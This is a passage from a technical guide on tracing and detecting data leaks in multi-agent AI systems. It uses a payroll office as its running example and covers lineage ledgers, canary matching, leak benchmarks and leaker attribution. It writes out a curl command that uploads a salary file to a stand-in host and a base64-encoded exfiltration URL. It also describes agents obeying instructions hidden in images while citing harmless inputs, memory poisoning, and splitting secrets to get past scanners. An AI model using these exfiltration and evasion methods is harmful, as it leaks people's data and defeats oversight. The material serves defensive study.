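An agent could fill in the parent calls itself, since it has just read the data. In *Deny Without Disabling*, Zhang, Lyu and colleagues (2026) tested how well this works by running 840 delegation graphs, each a task that passed through 1, 2, 4, 8 or 16 agents. Only the first agent received the original source, and each later agent received its predecessor's handoff. Seven teams of agents each ran 24 graphs at each size. Five teams used a single model (Claude Sonnet 4.5, Claude Haiku 4.5, Qwen3-32B, Gemma3-27B or Llama-3.3-70B), and two mixed models.

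Each agent had to report which item it had received, whether it had seen the original source, and how many transformations the data had been through. The researchers counted a lineage as complete only if every agent got all three right, which happened in 178 of the 840 graphs (21%). The finished work showed no sign of the failures, because the agents completed all 840 tasks and kept the label naming the origin every time.

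The measure is strict, so even if each agent had a 90% chance of getting its report right, a chain of 16 would be complete only about 19% of the time. Vague instructions also explain much of the result. In a separate comparison on new scenarios, the researchers gave agents either the data type of each field or its exact definition. Lineage was complete in 202 of 840 graphs with data types and in 834 of 840 with exact definitions.

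Exact definitions are clearly worth having, but they worked less well in a later development test, where agents given explicit definitions produced complete lineage in only 69% of graphs. The software running the agents recorded it correctly every time. Even in the comparison where 834 lineages were complete, at least one agent in 676 graphs misreported what permission an outside message claimed or how much authority the message had. These agents were cooperative, whereas a compromised agent could report whatever its attacker wanted.

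The gateway therefore has to supply a current policy decision as well. When Zhang and colleagues changed a permission during a task, agents that relied on a saved copy of the policy took a forbidden action in 120 of 240 runs, while agents that reread the policy did so in one run.

Lineage also matters when a record travels in pieces. If one agent sends "12" and another sends "34", neither message contains the access code 1234, but an agent that receives both can assemble it. In a controlled test, checks on individual messages let 413 of 480 forbidden actions through. A check on the combined messages stopped all 480, and permitted actions went through equally often under both checks. But the checker can combine the pieces only if it can identify which ones belong together. When the researchers divided a 16-field record among 15 agents, the checker could not identify the record in 19 of 168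 graphs, although every field had arrived.

### A ledger that works out dependencies itself

The gateway can avoid relying on agents if it controls the references they use. Yocam, Vaidyan and colleagues (2026), in *Agentic AI Defense*, built such a ledger to stop attackers who hide instructions in images, such as the logo in an email signature. Software between the agents and their tools keeps the ledger. Each time a tool returns a result, the software does the following:

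1. It finds the inputs. Agents refer to earlier results by handles, which are reference numbers that the software issued, so it can look up each one.
2. It marks the result "untrusted" if the tool decodes hidden or encoded content, or if any of the inputs was untrusted.
3. It signs the record with a key that the agents never see: `signature = HMAC(key, result | tool | label | origin | inputs)`.
4. It stores the record and, if the result is untrusted, adds it to a list of untrusted items that have entered the agent's context.
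5. It gives the agent a handle for the new result.

When an agent requests a consequential action, such as sending an email, the software follows the handles back through the ledger to every result they depend on. It blocks the call if a signature is wrong, an input is missing or any of those results is untrusted. It then checks the list for the agent's context and blocks the call if the list contains anything untrusted that nobody has cleared.

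The last check is for agents that read one thing and cite another. An agent might obey an instruction hidden in a logo but attach only the handle of a harmless settings file. This trick worked when Yocam and colleagues relied on the agent's own account of its inputs, but failed when they used the ledger. The signature guards against a different attack, in which a dishonest relay changes a label being sent to another organisation that has no access to the ledger. When the researchers removed the signature, the forged label got through.

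The software blocked all 24 test attacks, while a keyword scanner missed 15. But a simple tracker with no signatures also blocked all 24, so the ledger and signatures matter only when an agent or relay is dishonest. The tests were small and used one small model, so they mostly confirm that the logic works as designed. Signed labels remained valid after ten relays, and checking a call that depended on a hundred earlier results took about 0.7 milliseconds.

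The payroll office could use the same design with a "salary data" label in place of "untrusted". The ledger would then connect a summary to the salary file even if rewording had removed the fake number. But it would also flag too much, because once an agent had read the file, every later call from the same context would carry the label, even a request for the weather. A canary in the weather request would be much better evidence than the label that the request contained salary data. Yocam and colleagues had a similar problem with text recognition, which they class as decoding. Their software blocked a legitimate payment because the invoice number came from an image, until they added a way for an authorised person to clear it.

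The ledger also has no record of information that leaves by a route the software doesn't handle, for example when an agent paraphrases the salaries into a separate chat channel.

### Signed lineage for an agent's memory

Data can also stay in an agent's memory after a call ends. An agent that handled payroll in the morning might save a summary and retrieve it that afternoon for another job. In *Memlineage*, Ouyang and Hou (2026) present a system that preserves the link between saved data and the original call. They designed it to stop attackers who plant text in an agent's memory, but the method also works for tracing.

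Each memory entry contains its content, writer, time and trust level, along with hashes of the source data and of the prompt when the agent wrote it. It also lists its parent entries and gives each a weight from 0 to 1. The system builds and uses the entries as follows:

1. When the agent saves a note, the system treats the entries the agent has just retrieved as its possible parents.
2. It weights each parent by how much it influenced the note. The simplest method gives every parent a weight of 1. Another asks a second language model to judge.
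3. It gives the note the least trusted label found among the parents whose weight exceeds a threshold.
4. It signs the entry with the writer's private key and adds a hash of the entry to a log that accepts only additions. To delete an entry, the system adds a marker and leaves the original record in the log.
5. When the agent retrieves the note, the system checks the signature and the log, then attaches the label.
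6. Before a sensitive action, it checks whether the action relies on anything with an untrusted ancestor, and if so it can refuse.

In one scripted test, an agent summarised an outside company's document in its first session and retrieved only the summary in its second. A system that checked only signatures found a properly signed summary with no parents, and let the agent send an email it should not have sent. The lineage system still had the link between the summary and the document, and blocked the email. With a live model, gpt-5.3-codex, the agent sent the email in 5 of 20 trials without protection and in none of 20 with it.

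The weights are the weak point, because a parent whose weight is below the threshold doesn't pass on its label. With a threshold of 0.3, an untrusted parent with a weight of 0.5 passed on its label, but one with a weight of 0.2 did not, and the note counted as trusted. Repeated summaries can also bring the weight below the threshold. If the judge gives the first link a weight of 0.9 and each later link 70% of the one before, the fifth link has a weight of 0.9 × 0.7⁴, or about 0.22, and the connection to the source is lost.

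Giving every retrieved entry a weight of 1 is safer for tracing. The ledger will then list some ancestors that contributed nothing, but an investigator can rule those out later, whereas a missing ancestor may never be found. This doesn't help if the system fails to record a parent. Ouyang and Hou offer a strict setting that refuses sensitive actions based on notes without parents, but it also blocks ordinary instructions that the user saved directly.

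### Labels compared with canaries

Information-flow control uses lineage to stop a transfer before it happens. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes a system that labels every item of data, carries the labels over to anything derived from it, and checks them before each tool call. The labels record whether the data is trustworthy and who may read it.

In Microsoft's example, Alex asks an agent to answer some emails. One, from Priya, contains unreleased sales figures, and another is from Marco, who isn't allowed to see them. Alex and Priya may read the first email, and Alex and Marco may read the second. Once the agent has read both, only Alex may read what it writes, because only Alex may read both emails. The system therefore won't let the agent send its reply to Marco without asking, whether or not the reply mentions sales.

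The labels go in the same `_meta` field as the trace identifiers. Microsoft and GitHub have added experimental support for them to GitHub's command-line coding agent, under a setting named after FIDES, Microsoft's research system. Microsoft has also released a gateway that adds labels for servers that don't supply their own, but someone has to write a labelling function for each tool and write or choose a policy for it.

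CaMeL does the checking in a special Python interpreter, which runs the agent's plan and tracks everything that a tool call depends on, directly or indirectly. *Securing MCP-based Agent Workflows* (Ntousakis, 2026) describes SAMOS, which does the checking at an MCP gateway and labels whole tools instead of individual items. A developer or administrator marks the data that each tool reads and writes as high or low confidentiality, and the gateway tracks the session's level. Labelling tools is much less work than labelling every item, but cruder. A tool that reads both public and private files has to report which kind it has read, or the developer has to split it in two.

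All these systems have trouble with tools whose workings they can't observe. Li, Wang and colleagues (2026) argue in *PACE* that labels fail at such tools because every transformation would have to carry them forward. Their system records each call in an append-only log and compares the arguments of each new call with earlier records. It also recognises protected values in several standard encodings, but misses paraphrases, translations and fragments. Microsoft suggests assuming that everything sent to a tool may appear in its output, which prevents gaps in the lineage but restricts a lot of harmless data.

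If the labelling is correct, one label on the salary file protects all thousand salaries in every copy inside the system. Canaries cover only a sample of the file, so a partial leak may contain none of them. Unlike a canary, a label can also stop a leak.

But labels work only where somebody enforces them. Once the policy allows the text-recognition tool to receive the salary file, the tool's operator can copy the file to another server that ignores labels. Ntousakis assumes that tools behave correctly and don't try to leak data. A canary can test that assumption. The payroll office should therefore use labels to block forbidden transfers and canaries to follow the data through permitted ones. A canary that turns up in a forbidden place may also reveal an incorrect label.

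### When a broker keeps no trustworthy records

If another company runs the broker, the office can record what it sends and what comes back, but not what happens in between. *What the Middleman Delivers* (Wu, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) studied this problem in 20 relays, model routers that resell access to other companies' models. A relay decrypts each request before sending it on over a second encrypted connection, so it can read and change everything. If several intermediaries handle a request, the response may reveal a problem but not which intermediary caused it.

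Five of the relays reported between 4,200 and 60,000 more input tokens (the units of text that model companies charge for) than the model's maker did for identical requests. The researchers could not tell from outside whether the relays had added text to the requests or only changed the count.

The ledger should mark a stretch like this as unobserved. If it instead records a guess that the request went straight from the relay to the model's maker, an investigator who later relies on that guess could overlook another intermediary.

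Signed evidence from each party would narrow the gap. Suppose that every broker and tool on a route issued a receipt for each transfer, containing:

- a hash of the data it received
- a hash of the data it sent
- the name of the next recipient
- a hash of the previous receipt
- its own digital signature

The office could check that each party received what the previous one sent, and a missing receipt would show where the record stopped. No party could later alter its receipt without invalidating the signature. The receipts would need public-key signatures, not HMACs.

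Wu and colleagues summarise several such proposals. In one, the model's provider signs particular details of each response so that the client can detect later changes to them. Another adds a record of how intermediaries transformed the output, which matters because text extracted from a scan will never have the same hash as the scan. AEGIS runs the forwarding software in an enclave, a protected part of a computer that can prove which program it is running. The client checks this proof before sending anything readable. Other designs prevent the gateway's operator from accessing the protected software and its routing records.

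These proposals need the cooperation of a model provider or broker, and they protect only the details that somebody signs. An accurate receipt for the salary file would show that the broker passed it to the text-recognition tool at 10:04, but not whether the broker had also kept a copy. An enclave gives some assurance against such copying if outsiders can inspect the program and confirm that it doesn't store data or send it elsewhere, but that assurance ends when the file leaves the enclave.

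## Detecting a canary in messages, tool calls and memory

The ledger lists only the transfers that passed through the gateway. To find out whether a fake employee has turned up anywhere else, the payroll office has to search the finished spreadsheet and other places.

*AgentLeak* (El Yagoubi, Badu-Marfo and Al Mallah, 2026) distinguishes seven channels through which a multi-agent system can leak data. Its 1,000 test scenarios, in healthcare, finance, law and corporate administration, each have a task and a set of sensitive fields, typically 29, of which the agents need about three. Any other field that appears in a channel counts as a leak. The study used five models, all since replaced by newer ones: Claude 3.5 Sonnet, Llama 3.3 70B, Mistral Large, GPT-4o and GPT-4o-mini. The researchers ran each scenario with one agent and again with a coordinating agent and a worker. They obtained 4,979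 usable traces, each covering both runs of one scenario on one model. The table gives the results for the two-agent runs, except that the figures for tool inputs and logs come from a smaller test.

| Channel | Example in the payroll office | Share with a leak |
|---|---|---|
| Final output | The finished spreadsheet | 27.2% |
| Messages between agents | One agent's instructions to another | 68.8% |
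| Tool inputs | The scan sent to the text-recognition tool | 62% to 86%, depending on the model (100 scenarios each) |
| Tool outputs | The recognised text | No large-scale figure |
| Shared memory | A saved summary of the salaries | 46.7% |
| Logs | The gateway's debugging log | Higher than for tool inputs in the same scenarios |
| Saved files | A copy of the spreadsheet on a shared drive | No large-scale figure |

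Across final outputs, messages and memory, 68.9% of traces had a leak. A single agent leaked in 43.2% of its final outputs, so dividing the work among agents made leaks in the final output less common but created more places where data could leak. Attacks made little difference to messages between agents, which leaked in 69.3% of traces with no attacker and 66.3% of those with a strong one.

In 2,076 traces (41.7% of all traces), the final output was clean but a message or memory entry was not. A check on outputs alone would have missed about three in five of the traces with any leak. The paper mislabels the 41.7% as the share of violations that such a check would miss.

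Tool calls are harder to cover because an agent chooses which tools to combine as it works. *AgentRaft* (2026) presents a system that maps which tools' outputs can become another tool's inputs, then looks for routes along which an agent passes on more data than the task requires. The office could use such a map to decide which calls to search. For example, if an agent can read files and send emails, its emails need to be checked.

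Every trace with a leak in memory also had one in a message or the output, so searching memory would have found no additional cases. Searching it is still worthwhile because a saved entry can resurface in another task months later. *A Survey on Long-Term Memory Security in LLM Agents* (2026) describes agents that had no access to their usual memory and passed goals to later agents through shared files, so the search has to include those files.

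If another company hosts the memory and won't allow a search, the office can question the agent. The survey mentions MRM-MIA, which combines several recall questions to test whether a known item is in a chat agent's memory. The office should ask about the fake employee's department or job title and leave out the staff number, because including the number may add it to the memory.

### When an internal message counts as a leak

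The agents in these tests belonged to one system, so a message between them didn't necessarily reach an outsider. Such a message counts as a violation only under a strict data minimisation rule, which limits each agent to the data its task requires. El Yagoubi and colleagues accept this, and distinguish between breaking that rule, raising the risk that data will get out later, and an actual breach, in which somebody unauthorised receives the data. Their benchmark measures how often agents break the rule. They argue that this matters because EU data protection law and similar laws require minimisation, and because a compromised agent or a stray log could expose whatever the agents have over-shared.

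The 68.8% therefore measures over-sharing and is weak evidence of how often strangers obtain the data. For the payroll office, the allowed-flow map determines whether a canary in a message is a violation. A fake staff number sent to a scheduling agent is a violation if the agent may receive only staff names, but normal if it may receive the whole file.

### Three kinds of detector

El Yagoubi and colleagues used three detectors. Canary matching searches for unique marker strings that the researchers planted. Field extraction looks for anything in a known format, such as a US social security number. The third detector is a language model, Qwen-2.5-7B, which acts as a judge and compares the meaning of a passage with the sensitive fields, so it can recognise a paraphrase. The researchers compared them on 1,000 labelled passages:

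| Detector | Leaks found | False alarms on harmless passages |
|---|---|---|
| Canary matching | 8% | 0% |
| Canary matching and field extraction | 18% | 0.2% |
| Model as judge | 92.6% | 6.2% |
| All three | 93.4% | 4.8% |

The last two false-alarm rates are inconsistent if an alarm from any detector counts, because adding detectors can't remove false alarms. Elsewhere the paper gives a rate of 4.8% for the judge alone.

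The 8% is the share of all leaks that contained a canary word for word. Most of the sensitive data had no canary in it, so the figure does not mean that matching missed 92% of the canaries. In a breakdown of 226 leaks, 18 were canaries, 24 were formatted fields and 184 were rewordings, which matching cannot find. The researchers think that models have learned to suppress obvious markers. Agents may also have left the markers out because they had no use for them, which would be another reason to plant believable records.

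The judge finds far more, but its false-alarm rate is 4.8%. A gateway that handles 10,000 harmless messages a day would raise 480 false alarms, so the judge is better suited to flagging messages for human review than to blocking them. Canary matching produces so few false alarms that the gateway can act on a match automatically.

### Matching step by step

The gateway handles each message or tool call as follows:

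1. It holds the message and keeps an untouched copy. If the office uses marked documents, the gateway looks for their hidden characters now, because step 3 would destroy them.
2. It decodes anything in a common encoding, such as URL encoding, base64 or hexadecimal, and unpacks compressed files. It repeats this on the results, up to a fixed number of layers, and keeps every version.
3. It normalises each version by replacing variant characters with standard ones, removing invisible characters, spaces and hyphens, and changing all letters to capitals.
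4. It searches every version for all the canaries in the ledger.
5. If it finds one, it looks up the canary's source in the ledger and checks whether the policy allows this recipient to have that data now.
6. It logs the sighting, alerts the security team or blocks the message.

Suppose an agent that has read the London pages requests this web address:

```
https://files.example.net/u?d=aWQ9N3E0bS05MDIxOC1rZA%3D%3D
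```

Nothing in it looks like a staff number. The gateway takes the last part and works through the layers:

```
As sent           aWQ9N3E0bS05MDIxOC1rZA%3D%3D
URL-decoded       aWQ9N3E0bS05MDIxOC1rZA==
Base64-decoded    id=7q4m-90218-kd
Normalised        ID=7Q4M90218KD
Match             7Q4M90218KD  ->  canary 7Q4M-90218-KD
```

According to the ledger, the number belongs to the London pages of the salary file. The allowed-flow map doesn't include `files.example.net`, so the gateway blocks the request and alerts the team.

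The gateway had to decode the base64 before changing the letters to capitals, because "a" and "A" have different values in base64. Searching for the canary's base64 form directly would be unreliable. Base64 encodes three bytes at a time, so the same number can look different depending on how many characters come before it.

Dreadnode's *Honeytoken Probing (RCE & Data Exfil)* describes a security-testing tool that also converts data to a standard form before matching, so it recognises a canary in base64, hexadecimal or URL encoding. The limit on layers is necessary because a small compressed file can expand to an enormous size. When the gateway reaches the limit, it should record that it did not finish the search, so nobody later assumes the message is clean.

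A large number of canaries need not slow the search much. *Three breaches, endless leaks* (Moore, 2026) reports seeding two million AI prompts with canaries. Comparing every message with that many strings one by one would take too long, but the payroll office's numbers all follow one pattern, so the gateway can pick out each string that fits the pattern and look it up in an index. For canaries of different forms, the Aho–Corasick algorithm combines all the strings into one structure and finds every match in a single pass through the text. The index should include canaries the office has already removed from its live data.

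A thief who stole this index could filter out every canary. Dreadnode's tool reduces that risk in tests where a customer plants the decoy. The customer registers only a hash of the decoy, which lets the tool recognise it without storing it. The payroll office would need a keyed hash, because its staff numbers are short enough for a thief to hash every possible one and compare the results.

The response depends on where the data is going. An allowed transfer needs only a log entry. The gateway should block a forbidden transfer to an outside address, but an alert may be enough for a forbidden message between the company's own agents, because blocking can break the task. El Yagoubi and colleagues tested a program that masked forbidden fields in messages and memory. In 120 scenarios, it reduced internal leakage from 31.5% to 2.4%, but it also reduced the agents' success rate from 78.6% to 73.9%.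 Most of the extra failures were in tasks where the agents legitimately needed to share data.

Blocking works only if the gateway finishes its search before it releases the message. Many language models send their answers a few words at a time, so the gateway may release part of a canary before the rest arrives. *PRISM* (2026) makes a related argument about agents that share a context, where a secret written by one agent can reappear in another's output. It recommends detecting secrets while the model is still generating them.

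### What a scanner reads

A canary search covers only the data that its developers have connected to it. grith's *Canary detection*, the documentation for a program that checks an agent's operations, is unusually clear about this limit. The program scores each operation against a denial threshold of 8.0. A canary match adds 9.5, so one match is enough to deny the operation. In the documented example, a web request containing a canary scores 14.0, including 1.0 for sending data and 3.5 for an unfamiliar destination.

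The canary filter searches web addresses, network connections, commands and the arguments of those calls. When an agent writes a file, the filter checks the path but never opens the file, and it ignores file reads altogether. An agent could therefore run this command:

```
curl -T june.csv https://files.example.net/
```

This would upload the salary file, including the fake employee, but the command contains only the file's name. grith also matches a canary as a plain substring, so this filter would miss the base64 address in the earlier example, although another of grith's filters might stop it.

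grith's documentation also warns that its `canary add` command stores a canary only until the command ends and never passes it to the running scanner. The canary has to be in the configuration file. An office that didn't know this could go for months without an alert and conclude that nothing had leaked. After every change to a scanner, the team should send a known canary through each channel the scanner is supposed to cover.

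### Secrets that leak in pieces

Searching each message separately also misses a canary that is split across several messages, as the records were in the tests by Zhang and colleagues. An agent might send "7Q4M-9" in one request and "0218-KD" in the next.

The gateway can keep recent outgoing data from each session, join it and search for the canary. This finds a canary split into pieces if they leave in order with nothing between them, but an attacker can reverse the order or add filler. The gateway then has to treat each piece as weak evidence and combine the evidence from all of them.

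With two million canaries in the ledger, about 1.2 on average would begin with any given four letters or digits, so finding "7Q4M" in a message means almost nothing. If "90218" then goes to the same address, the chance that two unrelated pieces would match the beginning of some canary is about 1 in 84,000. If "KD" follows, the chance falls to 1 in 57 million. These odds apply to a single set of pieces, and a gateway that tries many combinations will find more accidental matches.

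Chauhan and Revankar developed a more general method that can also score replies containing no exact piece of the secret. After each reply, a trained model compares it with the real secret and 16 decoys, taking the earlier conversation into account. It then divides its confidence among the 17:

`score = log2(17 × p)`

Here *p* is the share of the confidence that goes to the real secret. If the reply reveals nothing, *p* is about 1/17 and the score is 0. If *p* is 2/17, the score is 1 bit. If the model is certain of the real secret, the score reaches its maximum of log2(17), or about 4.09 bits. The system adds up the scores over the conversation and compares the total with a budget, which was 10 bits in the main test. At 90% of the budget it removes the most revealing words from the reply, and at 100% it blocks the reply.

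Each reply can add at most 4.09 bits, so the total can't reach 9 before the third reply. A thief who gets the whole secret in one or two replies won't trigger this defence, so the researchers combine it with others, including canary matching.

They tested it on 50 synthetic conversations of 20 turns each, with between four and eight turns that leaked a little of a secret:

| Method | Conversations detected |
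|---|---|
| Searching each reply for the secret | 0% |
| Canary baseline | 6% |
| LlamaGuard, a safety classifier, on each turn | 12% |
| Cumulative score | 90% |

The cumulative score blocked nothing by mistake, but it detected the leak at turn 9 on average, after some of the secret had already been disclosed.

The study replaced hand-tuned thresholds for canary matching with conformal calibration, which sets the threshold from examples of harmless output. Suppose the detector gives a suspicion score to 999 harmless outputs. If the team sets the threshold at the 990th lowest score, a new harmless output has at most a 1% chance of exceeding it. This holds only if new outputs resemble the examples, and an attacker may deliberately make them differ. In a small test with a coverage target of 99%, calibration raised coverage from 98.4% to 99.8% but did not change precision or recall, which were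 already perfect.

In a separate test of single-turn attacks, the canary detector caught 30% with no false alarms. The full system caught 94%, with false alarms on 1.8% of harmless prompts. But it also inspects the model's internal activity, which a company can't do if it rents the model from a host. Without that inspection, detection fell to 71%.

The researchers call the results preliminary. They wrote the multi-turn test themselves, and the score is a learned signal that doesn't guarantee a limit on how much can leak. Most of the conversations that escaped detection leaked early and ended before the total reached the threshold. An attacker could also reset the total by starting a new conversation, unless the system stores it between sessions. The most serious gap for the payroll office is that the prototype doesn't examine tool-call arguments, and the salary file leaves the company through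 them. The researchers recommend extending both the canary search and the cumulative score to those arguments.

The gateway can also watch for the repeated prompting that such an attack requires. *LLM-enabled Applications Require System-Level Threat Monitoring* (2026) gives the example of an attacker who sends a customer-support agent 10,000 slightly different prompts, each asking it to complete a sentence from a confidential tax audit. Warning signs include a session whose prompts differ by only a few characters and a user who repeatedly stops just short of the request limit.

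### Alerts from live canaries

According to GitGuardian's *Understand honeytoken events and trigger mechanism*, an alert from one of its live canaries records the time, the IP address and country, the user agent (the visiting software's name for itself) and the action attempted. With a fake AWS key, the action might be `GetCallerIdentity`, which only identifies the key's owner, or `ListBuckets`, which lists the account's storage. In November 2026, GitGuardian added a decoy login for Kubernetes, a system for running software on many machines. The first attempt to use the decoy triggers an alert that identifies the source computer.

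A live canary can trigger an alert even when nobody has stolen anything. If a payroll clerk pastes a canary web address into a chat, the messaging app may fetch the page to make a preview. Bellingcat's *How To Blow Your Online Cover With URL Previews* (2019) shows that Apple's Messages app included the names of Facebook's and Twitter's crawlers in the user agent for such requests, so someone reading the log might suspect the wrong company.

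Security software also fetches links. According to CISPA, a German cybersecurity research centre, many companies automatically check links in employees' incoming email with services such as VirusTotal and URLScan. Some scanning services publish the links they check, so strangers who never had the salary file may visit them.

A language model may also open the address for a legitimate reason. If a clerk asks a chatbot to check the links in a document, the chatbot's host will fetch the canary. The fetch shows that the document reached the host, which the office's map may permit. The map should therefore state whether each recipient may open links.

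The user agent can't distinguish these cases from theft, because thieves can forge it. The thieves hrbrmstr observed used between 43 and 473 forged names in each run, including ChatGPT-User and Claude-User. The IP address is better evidence if the model's host publishes the addresses it uses. But the thieves rented their machines from Google, so an address belonging to a well-known company doesn't prove that the visit was innocent.

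GitGuardian's customers can tell the system to ignore known addresses, but the company warns that this may hide unauthorised use. If the payroll office ignored every visit from its model host, it would also miss any improper use of the data by that host. GitGuardian can instead label events from a known address and still raise the alert. It stops recording new events once a canary has 100 open ones, which can happen when a key appears on a public website and many scanners test it. A thief who tried the key after that would leave no record unless someone had reset the canary.

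### What to check first

An alert may be the first sign of a serious theft or the result of a colleague sharing a link. The team can work through it in this order:

1. If the canary is a key, replace any real keys stored beside it. A thief who took one probably took them all and may try them within seconds.
2. Save the alert, the message or page that contained the canary, and the ledger entry, before anyone deletes or resets anything.
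3. Confirm that the canary is genuine by checking the ledger and recomputing the keyed hash.
4. Check whether the map allowed this recipient to have the data at that time, and to keep it or open links in it.
5. Look for an innocent explanation. A single page fetch a second after a clerk sent a message is probably a preview. An attempt to list a company's storage is not, although an approved security tool may be responsible.
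6. Search for other canaries from the same file and for the real data that surrounded them, to find out how much leaked.
7. If the transfer was forbidden or remains unexplained, suspend that route at the gateway while the investigation continues.

Grafana Labs also isolates the affected systems at this stage, before an intruder can reach real data.

When several alerts arrive together, the team should begin with any key that someone has tried to use for more than a validity check. Salary data on an unfamiliar server comes next, followed by forbidden messages between the company's own agents. A single visit to a canary web address can usually wait, unless it came from an IP address that also appears in another alert.

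## Working out which intermediary leaked

Once the team has confirmed a sighting, it has to work out whose copy leaked, which is difficult when several companies held identical copies. *Lime* (Backes, Grimm and Kate, 2014) describes a leak that affected up to 108,000 Florida state employees. The outsourcing company that received their data had hired a subcontractor, which had hired another in India. Suspicion fell on the Indian company, but all three had held the data and nobody could prove which of them had leaked it.

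### A different canary for each recipient

The simplest remedy, which Spitzner described, is to put a different canary in each recipient's copy. *Countering financially-motivated malicious actors on the Internet* (DeBlasio, 2018) describes Tripwire, a large test of this design that DeBlasio and three colleagues first published in 2017.

Their software registered accounts at about 2,300 websites. It gave each account its own email address and used the same password for the website and the email account. Nobody had a reason to log in to these email accounts, so a login meant somebody had obtained the password, almost certainly from the one website that had it. By February 2017, the researchers had detected break-ins at 19 sites, including one run by a company with more than 45 million customers.

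The researchers also had to rule out a leak from their own records or from the email provider, so they kept more than 100,000 other email accounts that they never registered anywhere. Nobody logged in to any of them. The study used about 8,400 accounts. If a thief had stolen the whole list and picked 19 accounts at random, the chance of picking only used ones would have been less than 1 in 10¹⁹. The payroll office can do the same by adding fake staff numbers to its ledger and never planting them, so that if one turns up, the office knows the ledger has leaked.

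The researchers varied the passwords, which helped them infer how the sites had stored them. At most sites they tried to register one account with an easy password, such as `Website1`, and another with ten random letters and digits. At eight of the 19 sites, intruders got into only the account with the easy password. Those sites had probably stored their passwords in scrambled form, and the thieves had guessed the weak ones. At ten sites the intruders also obtained a hard password, which suggests that those sites had stored passwords in readable form or scrambled them badly.

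But identifying the site did not always show who had leaked the password. One outdoor-recreation site had changed hands, and the new owner was moving the site's accounts to another system around the time of the suspicious logins, so either company could have been responsible. Two gaming sites, each with its own canary, had the same owner and appeared to share a registration system, so a single break-in probably exposed both canaries. The researchers contacted 18 of the sites. Six replied, and only one confirmed a breach.

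The payroll office would have the same problem with the pensions adviser's copy. It could tell a theft at the adviser from a leak at the adviser's printing firm only if the adviser had planted its own canaries in the copies it passed on.

### Scoring recipients who held the same records

When a partial leak contains no canary, the team can compare the leaked rows with its records of who received which rows. Papadimitriou and Garcia-Molina's 2011 paper *Data Leakage Detection* gives a formula for doing this.

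Let *p* be the chance that a leaked item came from somewhere other than the recipients. If it did come from a recipient, the formula treats everyone who held it as equally likely to have leaked it. Each holder therefore leaked that item with probability (1 − *p*) / holders. Multiplying together the chances that a recipient did *not* leak each item gives the chance that it leaked none of them. Its score is the remainder:

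`score = 1 − product of [1 − (1 − p) / holders]`

The product covers every leaked item that the recipient held. Suppose that three rows have leaked and *p* is 0.5:

| Leaked row | Holders | Chance that A leaked it | Chance that B leaked it |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | A and B | 0.25 | 0.25 |
| 2 | A and B | 0.25 | 0.25 |
| 3 | A | 0.50 | 0 |

A's score is 1 − (0.75 × 0.75 × 0.5), or 0.72. B's is 1 − (0.75 × 0.75), or 0.44. The scores add up to more than 1 because A and B may both have leaked.

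Suppose the leak also includes a fake employee who was only in A's copy. Hardly anyone could have obtained that record elsewhere, so its *p* is close to zero. If it is 0.001, A's score rises to 0.9997.

*p* has to include the chance that a thief took the number from the payroll store, the gateway or the ledger, as well as the chance that somebody guessed it. If the team puts the chance of such a theft at 2% in total, the canary by itself gives A a score of 0.98, however long and random the number is. A semantic canary would usually need a higher *p*, because recovering it means scoring several properties of a text, as in *Who Owns This Agent?*, instead of finding an exact match.

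The formula also assumes that each item leaked independently, which is rarely true of files. Suppose ten leaked rows were in both A's and B's copies, and *p* is again 0.5. Each recipient scores 1 − 0.75¹⁰, or 0.94. With a hundred rows, both scores are almost 1, so both recipients look certain to have leaked. But a single break-in at either company would explain all hundred rows. If the whole batch came from one of the two, and the team has no reason to suspect one more than the other, each should score 0.5 however many rows there are.

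The score can overstate the case against a sole holder just as badly. If only A held the ten rows, its score is 0.999. But if the alternative source is an old backup that contains all ten, and the team thinks it is as likely a source as A, the correct figure is again 0.5.

The assumption also inflates B's score in the first example. B's score stays at 0.44 after the canary appears, even though A held all four leaked items and B lacked two of them. If the items leaked together, B can't have been the source.

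The team should treat rows that appear together as one event and ask which recipient's copy could have supplied all of them. It may also want to stop assuming that every recipient is equally likely to leak, since a company with a history of breaches deserves more suspicion. The scores are still useful for deciding whom to investigate first, but they are too sensitive to these choices to support an accusation.

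### Grids for scarce canaries

Fake staff numbers are easy to create, so the payroll office can give each recipient a different one. Live canaries may be harder to obtain. Arranging recipients in a grid reduces the number needed, because each recipient gets one canary shared by everyone in its row and another shared by everyone in its column.

For example, 1,024 recipients fit in a grid of 32 rows and 32 columns. The team creates one canary for each row and one for each column, or 64 in total, and gives each recipient the two for its row and column. If the canaries for row 5 and column 12 turn up, the suspect is the recipient in that row and column.

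*CanaryTrap* (Farooqi, Musa and colleagues, 2020) tested both designs on 1,024 Facebook apps that asked for the user's email address. Facebook's anti-abuse defences made it hard to create many accounts or to change an account's address often. For the one-per-recipient design, the researchers used a single Facebook account and changed its email address before installing each app. For the grid, they used two more accounts, one for the 32 row addresses and one for the 32 column addresses. They installed the apps in December 2018 and monitored the mailboxes for more than a year.

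In the one-per-recipient test, the researchers received 12,704 emails. The addresses they had given to 16 of the apps received mail from senders other than the app. Four of these cases were harmless, because the mail came from partners that helped run the service, which Facebook allows. Three of the addresses received malicious mail, including ransom demands. Even then the app might not be to blame, because, as Farooqi and colleagues point out, an app may legitimately give addresses to a bulk email service, which then leaks them.

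The researchers looked for mail from the same sender in one row mailbox and one column mailbox of the grid. They identified 9 of the 16 apps this way and wrongly accused none. They missed five apps that behaved inconsistently. Some apps in the study, for instance, wrote to only one of their two addresses or used a different sender for each. The researchers missed a sixth app because of a software fault and a seventh because of a clash between senders.

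Facebook's advertising tool also showed that nine advertisers with no apparent connection to any of the apps had uploaded the account's email addresses to target their advertisements. But it did not show which address each advertiser had used, so the researchers could not tell which apps had leaked.

The researchers also used the one-per-recipient addresses to test whether apps kept their promises to delete data. They reached the developers of 87 apps with deletion requests, and 29 confirmed that they had deleted the data. Thirteen of those apps sent more mail afterwards.

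A grid becomes ambiguous when more than one recipient leaks. Two leakers in different rows and columns expose two row canaries and two column canaries. These cross in four places, so the team has four suspects, two of them innocent. Three leakers can produce nine suspects. CanaryTrap had this problem when two apps sent mail from the same address, and the researchers discarded 12 emails to avoid blaming the wrong apps.

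A third set of canaries resolves the case of two leakers. The team numbers the rows and columns from 0 to 31 and adds each recipient's row and column numbers together, subtracting 32 if the total is above 31. It then creates one canary for each possible total, which brings the number of canaries to 96. Suppose the leakers are at row 3, column 10 and row 8, column 21:

| Suspect | Row | Column | Total | Has that total's canary turned up? |
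|---|---|---|---|---|
| Leaker | 3 | 10 | 13 | Yes |
| Leaker | 8 | 21 | 29 | Yes |
| Innocent | 3 | 21 | 24 | No |
| Innocent | 8 | 10 | 18 | No |

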